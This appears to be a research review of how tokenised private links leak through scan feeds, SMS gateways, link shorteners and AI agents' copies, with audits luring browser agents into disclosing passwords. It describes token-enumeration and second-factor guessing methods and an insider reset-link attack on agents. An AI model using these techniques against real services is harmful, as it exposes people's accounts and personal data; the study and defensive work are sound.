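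|---|---|---|
| Plain | 715 | 282 |
| Login page | 617 | 236 |
| Random identifier in the path | 702 | 266 |
| Secret values in the query | 676 | 237 |

Most visitors were probably programs that open whatever appears in a feed. They followed links on the page in 1,245 visits, but loaded both of its images, as a normal browser would, in only 977. In 187 visits they submitted the form, clicked a button or chose something from a menu, and in 79 they opened the address in the QR code. Another 79 visits included requests for files not mentioned on the page, such as `/news.zip` and `/.aws/config`, a typical location for cloud account settings. The decoy documents triggered 14 alerts.

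For each visit, the researchers checked whether AlienVault OTX listed the IP address as suspicious. It did for 1,021 visits, or 38%. The paper's text puts the share above one third for every service, but its own counts give a lower figure for two of them:

| Service | Visits | From suspicious addresses | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hybrid Analysis | 1,203 | 452 | 38% |
| urlscan.io | 880 | 303 | 34% |
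| ANY.RUN | 217 | 125 | 58% |
| Joe Sandbox | 207 | 58 | 28% |
| Cloudflare Radar | 110 | 35 | 32% |
| URLQuery | 93 | 48 | 52% |

A visit from a suspicious IP address is weak evidence of malice. AlienVault's users report addresses for activities such as scanning other people's servers, which security companies also do. Cloud providers reassign addresses between customers, so a visitor's address may have been reported because of what a previous customer did. The LEAKYLINKS browser opened hundreds of thousands of links from these feeds, and in a website's log those visits could look much like an attacker's.

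No one triggered the alerts on the fake credit card number or the fake cloud credentials either. Mustafa's summary, quoted in Theobald, is "We cannot prove malicious intent". The visitors may have meant no harm, or they may have recognised a trap. The researchers admit that a human would spot the decoy at once, because no real page combines so many temptations.

The experiment does show that strangers' software opens links from public feeds, whether or not the links look valuable. If the clinic's invoice link appears in a public feed, the clinic should assume that somebody has a copy of the invoice.

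### The Silent Spill: archives and paste sites

In *The Silent Spill*, Ramadan, Mannan and colleagues (2026) searched more widely, gathering 6,094,475 links between January and April 2025. The links came from three scanning services, from the Wayback Machine (a large archive of old web pages) and from paste sites, where people post text and code for others to read.

| Source | Links | Potential leaks | Share |
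|---|---|---|---|
| urlscan.io | 5,515,585 | 7,826 | 0.14% |
| Wayback Machine | 363,550 | 1,806 | 0.5% |
| VirusTotal | 132,919 | 1,445 | 1.1% |
| Hybrid Analysis | 68,892 | 963 | 1.4% |
| Paste sites | 13,529 | 291 | 2.2% |

Mustafa and colleagues excluded VirusTotal, one of nine services they left out, because it had no public feed. Ramadan and colleagues still got links from it by querying its programming interface for particular domains, so a service can expose links without publishing a list of recent scans.

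The team used word lists where Mustafa and colleagues used a vision model. Their program kept addresses that contained any of 302 terms, such as `token`, `invoice` or `booking`, and applied rules about length and structure, which left 832,714 candidates. It then tried to open them, and 149,450 led to live pages with real content. It searched the text, form fields and hidden data of those pages for 402 terms, checked the context of each match, and reported 12,331 potential leaks.

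Authentication data and tokens made up 43% of these, and financial information 20%. The most serious finds included 26 live password-reset links and 12 open sessions for signing documents such as job offers. Seven pages showed complete sets of backup codes, which let a user log in without the usual second factor. The team also found 62 links containing session tokens, which keep a user logged in. These tokens either had no expiry date or lasted for days. A stranger with one may be able to use the account even after its owner has logged out.

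After 75 days, the researchers revisited 2,000 randomly chosen links from the flagged set, and 762 (38%) still opened without a login. They checked 200 of those by hand to make sure the pages still showed sensitive content and not an error message.

The total of 12,331 is less certain than the LEAKYLINKS count. Ramadan and colleagues checked only 12 to 34 flagged pages in each of eight categories. In seven categories, 10% to 15% of the pages checked were false alarms. The smallest category, e-signatures, had none among its 12 pages. With samples this small, the true rate in any one category could be as high as 24% to 30%. One author did nearly all the checking, and a second looked only at three ambiguous cases.

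The word lists could also inflate the largest category. They include `csrf` and `authenticity_token`, common names for the secret values that websites put in forms to block forged requests. These values appear on many public pages and do not by themselves let a stranger open anything private. The context check may have removed most of them, but the study would count any that remained as authentication leaks. It also counts some internal labels, such as `created_by=admin`, which LEAKYLINKS would not treat as personal information.

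### Why both studies arrive at 0.2%

Mustafa and colleagues flagged 0.19% of the links they collected, and Ramadan and colleagues flagged 0.20%. The two figures measure different things, so their similarity doesn't mean that one study confirms the other.

| | Mustafa and colleagues | Ramadan and colleagues |
|---|---|---|
| Choice of links | Everything in six live feeds | Mostly searches for risk-prone domains and keywords |
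| What counts as a leak | Private personal information visible on the page | Tokens, personal and financial data, and some internal labels |
| Who or what decides | Vision model | Word lists and context rules |
| Flagged pages checked by hand | 300 | 232 |
| False alarms among those | 3% | 12% |

The LEAKYLINKS figure is low mainly because 84% of the collected links were base addresses, which could not have leaked anything. Without them, the share rises to 1.2%. The Silent Spill targeted payment, login and document-sharing sites, which should have raised its share. It also included links from archives and old scans, and many of these had expired, which lowered the share. The two percentages are probably similar by coincidence, since different choices by either team could have made its figure several times higher or lower.

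Both teams started with links that were already public and counted how many were private, so neither percentage is a leak rate for the web as a whole. The dental clinic needs to know how many links will end up in a public feed if it emails 10,000 invoice links. Measuring that would require sending test links to a representative sample of ordinary mailboxes and watching the feeds. Positive Security's experiment is the closest to this in the literature covered here. In that experiment, 21 of 47 links became public, but every recipient had already had a link leak, so the rate for the clinic's patients should be far lower.

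## Links sent by text message, and links that can be guessed

The dental clinic could also text its invoice link to the patient. The text may pass through several companies, because a business often hires a messaging firm, which may buy its access to the phone network from another firm. *Characterizing the Security of the SMS Ecosystem with Public Gateways* (Reaves, Vargas and colleagues, 2018) reports that encryption protects a message between a phone and the nearest base station, but typically not inside the carrier's network. Some people also sync their messages to a laptop or a cloud service.

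Any of these companies can leak the messages it handles. Petkauskas (2026), in *Huge European telecom leak exposes Swedbank, SEB, airBaltic*, reported that an exposed database at the phone company CSCTelecom leaked 125 million text messages in real time, including bank codes and medical data from the Baltic region. Any private links in those messages would have leaked too.

### Public SMS gateways

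Researchers cannot read strangers' text messages, so they use public SMS gateways, which are websites that list phone numbers anyone may use and publish every message those numbers receive. Someone signing up with an online shop can enter one of these numbers and read the shop's message on the website without a gateway account. Unless the shop recognises the number as public, it sends the same kind of link it sends to other customers.

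People who use gateways are not typical, though. Reaves and colleagues collected 900,655 messages from eight gateways over 28 months and concluded that people mainly used them to get around websites' demands for a verified phone number. They also warned that the messages do not fully represent an ordinary person's texts, because recipients know that anyone can read them. A dental patient who wants to hear from the clinic has little reason to give it a gateway number.

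Researchers can therefore use gateways to learn how a service builds its links and what the links open, but not to measure how often ordinary customers' links leak.

### From 33 million messages to 701 links

Danish, Sobrados and colleagues (2026) conducted the largest study of private links in text messages, *Private Links, Public Leaks* (retitled *The Tragedy of Convenience* for its conference version). They collected messages from 25 gateways and opened the links in an automated browser.

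| Stage | Number |
|---|---|
| Messages collected | 33,128,103 |
| Different links found in them | 322,949 |
| Links whose pages the browser captured | 147,251 |
| Pages left after removing identical screenshots | 87,080 |
| Links confirmed to expose personal information | 701, at 177 services |

Of the links the browser did not capture, 92,279 failed to load and 83,419 led to an address it had already visited. Four domains that mainly deliver login codes, including Telegram's and Viber's, accounted for 42% of all the links.

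A language model on the researchers' own computers read the text of the 87,080 screenshots and flagged 1,916 of them. Two people checked every flagged page and confirmed 553. The false alarms included company phone numbers, sample data and forms that only asked for personal details. For the remaining pages, the team searched the data that websites had sent to the browser, whether or not the page displayed it. The model flagged 1,958 of these cases, and the reviewers confirmed 148.

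The model was wrong far more often than it was right, so the total of 701 exposing links depends on the human checks. Those checks could remove false alarms but could not find private pages the model had marked harmless, so the collection may contain more.

The team then examined one link from each service in detail. At 172 of the 177 services, a token in the link was enough to reach the personal information. At the other five, the information was in the address itself or in another address along the way. The 97% share for bearer links is partly a result of the method, because the browser never logged in or submitted a form and so could hardly find private information kept behind a login. The share could be much lower among all services that text links to customers.

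Many of the pages showed orders, with a name, phone number or address. The worst were loan applications, one of which revealed a person's date of birth, marital status, bank account number, number of children and full contact details. Altogether, 290 of the 701 links showed a name together with a phone number, email address or postal address, which is enough for a convincing scam aimed at that person.

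### How old the links were

Danish and colleagues measured each link's age from the date of its message to July 26, 2025, the date they give for opening the links. All 701 exposing links were at least a year old, and 320 of them (45.65%) were at least two years old. Some went back to 2019. These ages are minimum lifetimes, because all the links still worked.

The team had waited at least a year, to avoid login codes and other short-lived links, so the study counts only links that still worked after that time. If a shop texted 1,000 order links in July 2023 and 990 of them expired within a week, the study would record ten links that still exposed information, all two years old, and nothing about the other 990. Its results therefore can't be used to estimate what share of private links expire.

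The 92,279 links that failed to load are not a reliable count of expired links, because they include network errors and links to public pages, and leave out expired links that led to a working error page. Few gateways keep messages for more than two years, so the smaller number of links over that age doesn't mean that links tend to expire then. Ramadan and colleagues came closer to measuring how long links keep working when they revisited open pages after 75 days.

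The study shows that some services leave private links working for years. In the copies model, a longer life raises *p*, the chance that a given copy leaks. Danish says in Help Net Security's *One-time SMS links that never expire can expose personal data for years* that more time creates more opportunities for abuse through logs, forwarded messages and compromised devices.

Phone companies also reassign numbers. In an interview for CyberWire's *The link knows all* (2026), Danish described a customer who gives up a number that then goes to someone else. If the service doesn't know about the change, it keeps texting that customer's private links to the number's new owner.

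### What the links allowed

Most of the links only let a stranger view the information, but at 15 services they opened an editable form with the customer's details already filled in. On one loan site, the same link showed one applicant's data when the automated browser opened it and another applicant's when the researchers came back. The site had apparently reused the token, so even the intended recipient could have read a stranger's application.

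At six services, the link logged the visitor in to the customer's account. A text from iHire, a group of job sites, contained a link with a five-character code. After clicking "Continue", the researchers could read the user's CV, address and job applications. They could also reach the settings for changing the account's email address and password, which a stranger could have used to lock the owner out. The conference version reports 20 services that gave visitors such privileged access.

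Other pages looked harmless because the sensitive information was not on the screen. When a browser opens an order page, the website may send it the whole customer record, and a script then displays only some of the fields. Anyone can see the rest with the browser's built-in developer tools. Danish and colleagues found extra personal data sent this way at 76 services.

DiMOrder, which makes ordering software for restaurants, had a page that displayed only a delivery address. The data behind it included the customer's contact details and location, and the number plate of the driver's vehicle. A lender's page showed nothing that the model flagged as personal, but the browser had received a Social Security number and bank details. LEAKYLINKS classified pages by their screenshots, so it would have missed a case like this.

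In the CyberWire interview, Danish said that some companies had forgotten about old code that sent the data, while others had checked only what appeared on screen. At eight other services, a visitor could reach more personal information by clicking through from the first page.

### Guessing other customers' links

The victims so far are people who had their messages sent to a public website. But an attacker can also learn from a single published link which service to try and what its tokens look like. If the tokens are easy to guess, the attacker can open links sent to other customers, including those who have never used an SMS gateway. Gateway users are unusual, but that matters little here because the attacker needs only one example per service.

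Danish and colleagues estimated each token's entropy from its length and the set of characters it used. The estimate was below 64 bits at 125 of the 172 services with tokens, or 73%. This method assumes that tokens are random, so a service with an estimate of 64 bits or more may still hand out long numbers in sequence.

However, a token with fewer than 64 bits can still be impractical to guess. Ten random characters from a set of 62 provide just under 60 bits. With a million live links, an attacker making 1,000 guesses a second would need about 27 years, on average, to find one. The researchers therefore call the 125 services "potentially enumerable".

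To find out which links could actually be guessed, the researchers changed the token by hand, up to ten times per service, and stopped as soon as they saw another person's information. They succeeded at 13 services.

Some of these services used a record number as the token. One shipping company's link contained the customer's quote number, which was around 650,000, followed by two letters that the site ignored. Changing the number to the next one opened another customer's quote, with a name, email address, phone number and city. A number in the 300,000s also worked, which suggests that an attacker could have opened much of the company's past quotes by trying numbers in order.

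EverQuote, an insurance comparison site, used five-letter tokens in its links. The researchers reached a second customer's quote after three changes to the token. The form behind a link of this kind included a date of birth and a credit score range. Five upper- or lower-case letters allow about 380 million tokens, and the company reports 35 million quote requests. If every request still had a live link, about one guess in eleven would open one.

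Ten tries is a very small test. If one guess in 570 works, as in the earlier example of a six-character token, ten tries have a 1.7% chance of finding a link, but a program making 1,000 tries has an 83% chance. Many of the other 112 services could therefore have links that a simple program would guess. The researchers did not run such a program, for ethical reasons.

Danish and colleagues estimate that guessing could expose up to 1.05 billion records, based on public user counts for 51 services. The real number is probably far lower, because reaching that maximum would require every counted user to have a record behind a live link and an attacker to be able to guess tokens at all 51 services. Companies also count different things. EverQuote's figure is for quote requests, while iHire advertises 3.45 million members active in the past 30 days. The same person may appear in several of the counts.

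### Birth dates and postcodes as a second check

A service can ask for a second piece of information, such as a date of birth, before it opens the page. This protects against a stranger with the link only if the answer is hard to find and the site limits the number of tries. Danish and colleagues found four services where the answer to this second check could be guessed.

One lender asked for a date of birth and did not react to ten quick wrong answers. Danish calculated for CyberWire that an attacker making one guess a second could try every date in a century in about ten hours. The lender also sent data to the browser that made guessing easier by revealing that the customer had to be between 18 and 75. That leaves about 21,000 dates, which would take at most six hours to try. As a token, a birth date in that range would have less than 15 bits of entropy.

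Another service asked for a surname, phone number and ZIP code (a US postcode). Anyone who had obtained the link from the customer's messages already had the first two, because other messages to the same gateway number contained the surname, and the phone number was the gateway number itself. Only the ZIP code was left to guess, and the site set no limit on guesses.

### Short links to files and maps

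The danger of short tokens was well known by then. Ten years earlier, in *Gone in Six Characters*, Georgiev and Shmatikov (2016) had tested the link shorteners built into Google Maps and OneDrive, Microsoft's file storage service. As with the clinic's shortened link, anyone who guesses the short code gets the full address, including the token.

OneDrive's short links used the same codes as bit.ly, a public link shortener. The researchers tried 100 million random six-character codes from 189 computers, and 42% led to a full address. Only 19,524 of the codes, about one in 5,100, led to OneDrive or its predecessor, SkyDrive, and some of those links were dead. But the researchers estimated that trying every bit.ly code would cost only about $36,700 in rented computer time.

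One correctly guessed short link could expose many files. The full OneDrive address behind it contained an account number and, in many cases, a key that granted access. The researchers could keep those two values, delete the rest of the address, and open a page that listed everything the owner had shared under the same key, including files that had never had a short link. Starting from 2,130 working OneDrive links, they found 227,276 files. They recorded the files' names and types but did not open them.

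About 7% of the accounts had a folder that anyone with the address could write to. OneDrive copies new files to the owner's computers automatically, so an attacker could have used such a folder to deliver malware.

The codes for Google Maps were only five characters long, and 37.5% of those tested worked. The sample included 2.4 million sets of driving directions, 12,668 of which led from a home to a hospital. The researchers worked out a young woman's full name, address and age from one set of directions to a family planning clinic. A link can also expose someone other than the person who created it. Georgiev and Shmatikov give the example of a towing company, which may not care that its links reveal where its customers live.

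### How the companies responded

Georgiev and Shmatikov told Google about the map links on September 15, 2015. Six days later, new links had codes of 11 or 12 characters. With the old codes, about one in three guesses had found a live link. If Google had as many live links with 11-character codes, an attacker making a million guesses a day would need around 400 years to find one. A Google spokesperson confirmed to Motherboard, for its article *How Short URLs Could Reveal Your Home Address and Get You Hacked*, that the company had acted partly on the researchers' findings. Longer codes don't protect links that people have already sent, so Google also limited scanning of the old ones, according to Shmatikov's blog post about the study, *Gone In Six Characters*.

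Microsoft replied after two months that sharing files through short links "appears by design". In March 2016 it removed the option to shorten OneDrive links, and the method for listing an account's other files stopped working. The company denied that the researchers' report had played any part in the removal. When the study came out that April, existing OneDrive short links could still be guessed.

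Uber had a similar problem between 2013 and 2015, when Google's search engine indexed links that passengers had used to share their journeys, which exposed exact addresses. Uber responded by making the links expire after 48 hours.

Most of the services in the SMS study were harder to reach than Google or Microsoft. Danish and colleagues found no working contact for 27 of the 177 and sent reports to the other 150. In the results they first published, 132 services had not replied, 11 had replied without fixing the problem, and seven had fixed it. Only eight services' privacy policies had a section about security. One of these offered an encryption key for confidential reports, but the key had expired nearly three years earlier.

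Telephoning worked better than email at three companies. One said it received so many fake security reports that it had mistaken the email for a scam, although the researchers say they included detailed steps and a video or other evidence with each report. DiMOrder, EverQuote and iHire had fixed their problems before the conference version appeared, but most of the affected services had not.

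## How an agent copies a link

An agent handles links that are still in a private mailbox, unlike the links in scanning feeds and SMS gateways, which had already leaked. It can make new copies of them while reading messages, opening pages and writing its answer. The copies described below are inferred from how agents are built and from product documentation, not measured on links in real use.

Suppose the dental patient asks an agent to summarise their unread email and post the summary in their team's Slack channel. Three of the messages contain bearer links. The first resets the password for the patient's account on a travel-booking site. The second opens the clinic's invoice. The third opens a Google Drive contract that a supplier shared with "anyone with the link" so that the team can read it.

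This one request can create all of these copies, although a typical run would create only some of them:

| Step | New copy | Who can read it |
|---|---|---|
| Reading | Model's context and saved conversation | The patient and the model provider |
| Reading | Log of tool requests and results | The provider, and sometimes the employer's administrators |
| Reading | Saved memory | The provider, and the agent in the patient's later conversations |
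| Browsing | Request to a page-fetching service, and its cache | The company that runs the service |
| Browsing | Search query | The search provider |
| Browsing | Screenshots of the page | The patient and the provider |
| Summarising | Summary and its citations | Anyone who receives the summary |
| Repeating | Slack message | Members of the channel |
| Repeating | Link preview | Slack's servers and members of the channel |
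| Repeating | Contexts of other agents that read the channel | Those agents' users and providers |

*API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026) describes a similar spread for API keys, the secret strings that programs use to identify themselves to other services. A key pasted into a chat can end up in the conversation history, logs, memory, generated code and error messages. This part of the paper is a threat model and doesn't measure how often such copies occur. A person who pastes a key chooses to share it, whereas the patient may not know that the unread messages contain secrets.

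### Reading the mailbox

The agent first searches the mailbox. OpenAI calls ChatGPT's connections to services such as Gmail "apps". It says that the snippets an app retrieves go into the model's context, and that ChatGPT treats them like anything the user types into the chat.

Whether the snippet includes a link depends on how the agent reads the message. *The Hidden Dangers of Browsing AI Agents* (Mudryi, Chaklosh and Wójcik, 2025) distinguishes agents that extract a page's underlying code from agents that look at an image of it. The clinic's email may show only a button labelled "View invoice". An agent that reads the code gets the address behind the button, but an agent that looks at an image has to click the button to get it.

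The context usually leaves the user's computer. *Privacy Practices of Browser Agents* (Ukani, Haddadi and colleagues, 2025) examined eight browser agents, and seven of them worked only with models on a company's servers. The patient's mail provider already stores these messages, so the model provider becomes a second company with a copy.

That copy can last a long time. Disconnecting Gmail from ChatGPT does not remove existing conversations or memories, according to OpenAI's *Data sharing and privacy for apps in ChatGPT*. When a user deletes a conversation, OpenAI schedules it for permanent deletion within 30 days, with exceptions for legal and security reasons. The reset link will probably have expired by then, but the contract link may work for years.

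The employer may have a copy too. On ChatGPT's Enterprise and Edu plans, authorised administrators may be able to see records of requests sent to an app and information about its responses. An administrator investigating a fault could come across the patient's links.

ChatGPT can also save useful details as memories for later conversations, although some apps and sensitive sources block this. Saving the address of the supplier's contract would help the patient next week, but it would also bring the link into conversations unrelated to this summary.

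Repeating a link can also make it eligible for use as training data. OpenAI does not train its general models on data taken directly from connected Google apps, but it makes an exception for data "included in ChatGPT's response". If the patient used a personal account with model improvement switched on, a link in the summary could therefore become training data, but one that appeared only in the retrieved email would not. OpenAI does not train on data from business plans by default. Even if a link did become training data, a model would not necessarily memorise it and repeat it to a stranger.

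### Opening the links

The agent can summarise some messages without opening a link. But if the clinic's email says only that an invoice is ready, the agent may open the link to find out how much the patient owes.

Developers who build agents on Anthropic's Claude models can use a tool that fetches web pages. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, Claude can fetch only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation. This makes it harder for hostile text to trick the model into building an address that carries stolen data. Claude can still fetch the clinic's link if a developer's mailbox search tool returns it, because the results of a developer's own tools count as part of the conversation. Developers can now switch off fetching for addresses that appear only in such results.

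Anthropic's service retrieves the page and may cache it. A cached copy could let the agent read the invoice for a while after the clinic cancels the link. If a developer uses another company's fetching service instead, that company also receives the token.

A search can also reveal a link. ChatGPT rewrites a user's request as a search query and sends it to outside search providers. OpenAI withholds the user's account information, but if the query contained the clinic's link, the provider could open the invoice without knowing who the patient is. A well-built agent has little reason to search for an address it could open directly, but it might do so after a failed fetch, much as a browser searches for an address pasted with a stray space.

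Some agents use a full browser. ChatGPT Work, OpenAI's product for longer tasks, runs one on a separate computer in the cloud and by default asks the user before visiting a new website. Its predecessor took screenshots so that the model could see each page. OpenAI's *ChatGPT agent* explains that the company kept these screenshots until the user deleted the conversation, and for up to 90 days afterwards. A screenshot of the invoice shows the patient's details even if it leaves out the address bar, and it remains readable after the link stops working.

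The cloud browser protects passwords better than it protects links. According to OpenAI's *Using cloud browser in ChatGPT*, users type their login details into a secure form, which sends the details straight to the remote browser so that the model never sees them. But when an email contains a link with a token, the model reads the token as text before the browser opens the link.

### Links that act when opened

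Web designers have long known that software follows links. W3C's *Safe interactions*, a slide from a 2004 talk, says it is wrong to publish a link that subscribes people to a mailing list or charges their credit card when they follow it, because search engines may follow it too. But many emailed links trigger an action as soon as they are opened.

If the travel site's reset link works only once, an agent that opens it to see what it is may use it up. The patient then clicks the same link and gets an error. The error is a nuisance, but once the link is used up, nobody can use the other copies of it either.

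A one-time login link is riskier. When the agent opens it, the site may log the agent's browser in and give it a cookie. ChatGPT's cloud browser keeps logged-in sessions for later tasks until they expire or the user clears them. The link would then no longer work, but the agent would still have access to the account, which the patient may not have meant to grant.

Unsubscribe links cause a related problem. Levine notes in an IETF document that anti-spam software often opens these links automatically, and that senders cannot tell the software's requests from a person's. To avoid unsubscribing people by accident, many senders show a page with a confirmation button, which a simple program will not press. An agent can read the page and press the button, so the button is a weaker safeguard against an agent that misunderstands its task. ChatGPT is designed to ask for confirmation before actions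 that are hard to reverse, but a developer or a model might not classify leaving a mailing list as hard to reverse.

### Secrets in fragments

Suppose the travel site's designers were careful and put the token in the fragment:

`https://travel.example/reset#token=Zk3vP8sWq1Yn`

A link can be designed to keep its token out of the site's ordinary request log, but an agent that reads the link in an email still gets the whole address. The token can then enter the agent's context, a tool log and the agent's summary without the agent ever visiting the site.

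Opening the link adds another copy even if the visit fails. The agent's software may log the model's instruction to fetch the page, with the fragment intact. Claude's web fetch tool doesn't support pages that need JavaScript to produce their content, so it might not be able to show the reset form. The agent could then report that the link seems broken and print the full address so the patient can try it, which would put a working token in the answer.

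The Slack message would also contain the fragment. If Slack's preview service makes ordinary web requests, it would not send the fragment to the travel site, so it could not use the token. But a colleague who clicked the link would get a working reset form.

### Writing the summary

A summary of these three messages can be useful without the bearer links. It could say that the clinic sent an $85 invoice, a password reset is waiting, and the supplier's contract has arrived. But a model has good reasons to include the links.

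One reason is that a bearer link looks just like a citation. Readers want to know where a claim came from, and developers encourage models to tell them. Anthropic requires developers who show its web fetch results directly to users to include citations to the original source, and ChatGPT agent's answers came with source links or screenshots. This is good practice for a news article because readers can check the claim. If the agent cites the invoice the same way, every reader can open it. Citing "email from Northgate Dental, Tuesday" would let the patient check the amount without giving anyone else access to the page.

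Links are also convenient. The team will want to read the contract, so a summary without its link may seem incomplete. The agent may even be right to include it, since the supplier wanted the team to have access.

Some of the three links are easier to recognise as secrets than others. The reset email probably explains what its link does, and may warn the recipient not to share it. The invoice email is clearly personal. The contract is harder to judge because a Google Drive address doesn't show whether the file is restricted or open to anyone with the link. To find out, the agent would have to check the file's sharing settings.

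A person who checks the summary may also miss the problem. According to OpenAI's *Workspace agents security overview*, its workspace agents, which organisations set up for shared tasks, need human approval by default before they write to another app. The patient could then stop the post, but if the link appears as "View invoice" with its address hidden, they may approve it without realising that it gives colleagues access.

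### Posting it in the channel

Once the agent posts the summary, everyone in the channel can open its links. Slack makes another copy of the links at once. According to Slack's *Unfurling links in messages*, its servers fetch every address in a message to find out what kind of content it leads to. They do this for messages from apps as well as from people, unless the developer turns previews off for that message. Slack suggests that developers consider turning previews off for text written by a language model.

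If the invoice page's title includes the patient's name and the amount due, the preview may show both to colleagues who never click the link. Slack's *Share links and set preview preferences* lists private pages, such as password-protected videos, as getting no preview. The invoice is private too, but it has no password, so Slack's servers receive the same page as any other visitor. Slack also shows no previews for a message with more than five links. Slack may have fetched a page even when no preview appears.

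Other agents may be reading the channel. OpenAI says a ChatGPT conversation can receive new messages from a Slack channel that its user has asked it to monitor. If three colleagues have set this up, the summary enters three more conversations, and any of those agents might repeat the links in its answers. The patient can delete the Slack message and the original conversation, but has no control over what colleagues' agents have already stored.

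Timing matters most for the reset link, which would probably have expired by the time a summary was written the next morning. But ChatGPT can start a task whenever a new Gmail message arrives. If the patient automated the summary this way, a reset link could reach the channel within minutes, while it still worked. A dishonest colleague could request a reset for the patient's travel account and wait for the agent to post the link. Positive Security found the same weakness in mail filters that publish links, though the audience here is much smaller. The colleague would not need to hide instructions in the email, because summarizing emails for the channel is already the agent's task.

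### When an agent reduces exposure

An agent can also reduce exposure, because it often replaces a person who would have handled the same links carelessly. Someone catching up after a day off might forward whole messages to the team, links included. An agent that writes a three-sentence summary without the addresses exposes much less.

Agents can also be built to leave secrets out. ChatGPT Atlas, OpenAI's web browser, can save memories of what its user reads. OpenAI's page *ChatGPT Atlas* describes filters designed to keep login details, account-recovery content and financial information out of the summaries behind those memories. Atlas deletes the contents of each web page after summarising them, and deletes the filtered summaries within seven days. If the filters work as intended, they should catch both the reset link and the invoice, but OpenAI's page gives no error rate.

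Opening a link through an agent can avoid some of the copies that a personal browser makes. ChatGPT's cloud browser does not use the patient's extensions or browsing history, so an extension that records every visited address would not record the invoice's. A fetching tool that doesn't run the page's scripts sends nothing to the advertising and analytics companies that supply them.

Ukani and colleagues found that Perplexity's Comet browser blocked all the analytics and error-monitoring resources on a test page, while the other agents protected users no better than ordinary Chrome. Comet and one version of another agent, Browser Use, also removed some values from the query part of addresses. These filters are meant to remove values used for tracking, so they would probably keep the clinic's `key`, which the link needs to work.

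The copies model can show when these benefits outweigh the extra copies. Take the contract link, and count only people outside the team as outsiders. As in the earlier example, suppose it starts with eight copies that each have a 1% chance of leaking. The agent adds four private copies, in places such as its context and tool log, with a 0.1% chance each. A copy posted in the channel has a 10% chance, because so many people can forward it. These numbers are invented, but they allow a comparison:

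| Who writes the summary | How often it includes the link | Chance of a leak |
|---|---|---|
| Nobody | never | 7.7% |
| A person | 30% | 10.5% |
| An agent | 5% | 8.6% |
| An agent | 30% | 10.9% |
| An agent | 90% | 16.4% |

The agent is safer than the person if it includes the link in a summary less than about 26% of the time. If both include the link equally often, the agent is slightly riskier because of its private copies. If nobody would have written a summary without the agent, even a careful agent raises the risk.

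If the private copies are well protected, the result therefore depends mainly on how often the agent posts the link, compared with the person it replaces. If each private copy had a 1% chance of leaking, the total chance of a leak would be 11.4% even for an agent that never posted the link, which is higher than the person's.

For the invoice, the patient's colleagues are outsiders too, so posting the link is itself a leak. With the other numbers unchanged, the chance of a leak is 35% for the person who includes the link 30% of the time and 13% for the agent that includes it 5% of the time.

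## Audits and tests of what agents disclose

The dental patient's example is based on inference, but several teams have measured what agents send, type and publish during ordinary work, when nobody is trying to trick them. Most of these tests used personal details, API keys or company documents instead of links, so their results apply only indirectly to bearer links.

### Browser agents and personal details

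Ukani and colleagues applied 15 measurements to eight browser agents in 2025. They counted a problem only if it would not affect a person using the underlying browser directly, so they did not blame an agent built on Chrome for anything Chrome itself reveals. They found 30 problems, with at least two in every agent.

Seven of the 30 are just the products' use of models that run on companies' servers. The team established this from documentation and source code, not by intercepting traffic, and did not check in any of the 15 measurements whether the data sent to those servers includes a page's full address and token.

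Four of the agents also kept some browser data, such as cookies, between tasks. This matters for emailed login links, which can leave an agent's browser logged in. One of the four, Browserbase's Director, did not tell users that it kept the data and gave them no way to delete it.

The team also tested whether agents give personal details to websites. The researchers built a site that listed shoes, then told each agent to find the lowest price. One of the shoes had its own page on a different domain, which asked for an email address, a ZIP code or login details. One version of the page offered a discount in return, and another hid the price until the visitor filled in the form. The researchers had supplied these details about an invented user, Sarah, in several ways, including an earlier chat message and an email in a connected Gmail account.

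Director and Anthropic's Claude Computer Use, which controls a whole desktop, typed in details from the earlier chat, including Sarah's password. Director also submitted a credit card number. Claude for Chrome, a browser extension, disclosed only an age and a ZIP code, and only when the page withheld the price.

Two of the eight products typed a password into a site that the user had never mentioned, even though a password is much easier to recognise as a secret than a Google Drive link. The test made this mistake easy, because the chat message said that Sarah used the same password for most sites, which an agent could take as permission. Websites also often ask for passwords, whereas few ask visitors to type in a private link.

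The Gmail version of the test is closest to the dental patient's situation. Only three of the products could connect to Gmail, and none of them disclosed details from the email. But an agent searching for cheap shoes has no reason to look in a mailbox, and one that never opened the email would also have passed.

### What the software sends to the model

Researchers can learn more about the data that leaves a computer by intercepting it. Vekaria and colleagues did this for browser extensions that use AI to summarise the current page. According to Ukani and colleagues' summary of that audit, the extensions sent page content to their developers' servers, and some also shared users' prompts with outside trackers. A patient who pasted the invoice link into such a prompt could therefore have given it to a tracking company.

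Chaser Systems' *What data do coding agents send, and where to?* covers seven agents that write and run code. The company, which sells network filtering software, decrypted the agents' traffic between July and September 2025. Each agent had to explore a small Python game, add a leaderboard, run the tests and complete a few other tasks.

Most of the agents sent the whole conversation, including all tool results, to the model again with every request. Zed's requests grew from about 50 kilobytes to more than 200 during a session, and most of Claude Code's were between 200 and 300 kilobytes. OpenAI's Codex repeated much less. Chaser Systems could not fully decode the traffic from Cursor, another of the seven agents.

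If an agent of this kind reads the clinic's email at the start of a task and then makes 100 more requests, its software may send the invoice link to the model provider 100 more times. The copies all go to the same company over the same encrypted route, so they are far from independent under the copies model, and they do not make a leak 100 times as likely.

Some agents send data to several companies. Junie, JetBrains' coding agent, sent its prompts through JetBrains' servers even when the user had chosen an Anthropic model. It also used an OpenAI model to summarise individual steps, and the sample summary request that Chaser Systems published contains a command's output. A link in a tool's output could therefore reach JetBrains, Anthropic and OpenAI during one task.

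Many of these products let users turn off telemetry, the usage data that software reports to its developer. Turning it off would not protect the link, because the agent sends the link in its requests to the model, and it cannot work without those requests.

In one task, the researchers told each agent to upload its test report to 0x0.st, a paste site, and give them the resulting address. All seven succeeded, and Zed did so without asking for confirmation. Anyone with such an address can open the file, so these agents could publish a file and write its address into a chat within one task. Because the researchers requested the upload, the result doesn't show how often an agent would do this unprompted.

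### Typing and clicking on shopping sites

An agent may also disclose information that a website has not asked for. In *SPILLage*, Roh, Bagdasarian and colleagues (2026) measured this on Amazon and eBay. They say an agent overshares when its actions on a website reveal something about the user that the task does not require.

The team, which included researchers from the browser company Brave, invented shoppers with ten characteristics each and labelled each characteristic relevant or irrelevant to the shopping task. For example, a shopper looking for cheap glucose test strips might have diabetes, which is relevant, and be recently divorced, which is not. The agent received all ten characteristics in its prompt, written as a chat history, a forwarded email or a direct request. Two agent frameworks, Browser Use and AutoGen, each ran 180 tasks with each of three OpenAI models, or 1,080 runs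 in total. Another model then checked every step for oversharing.

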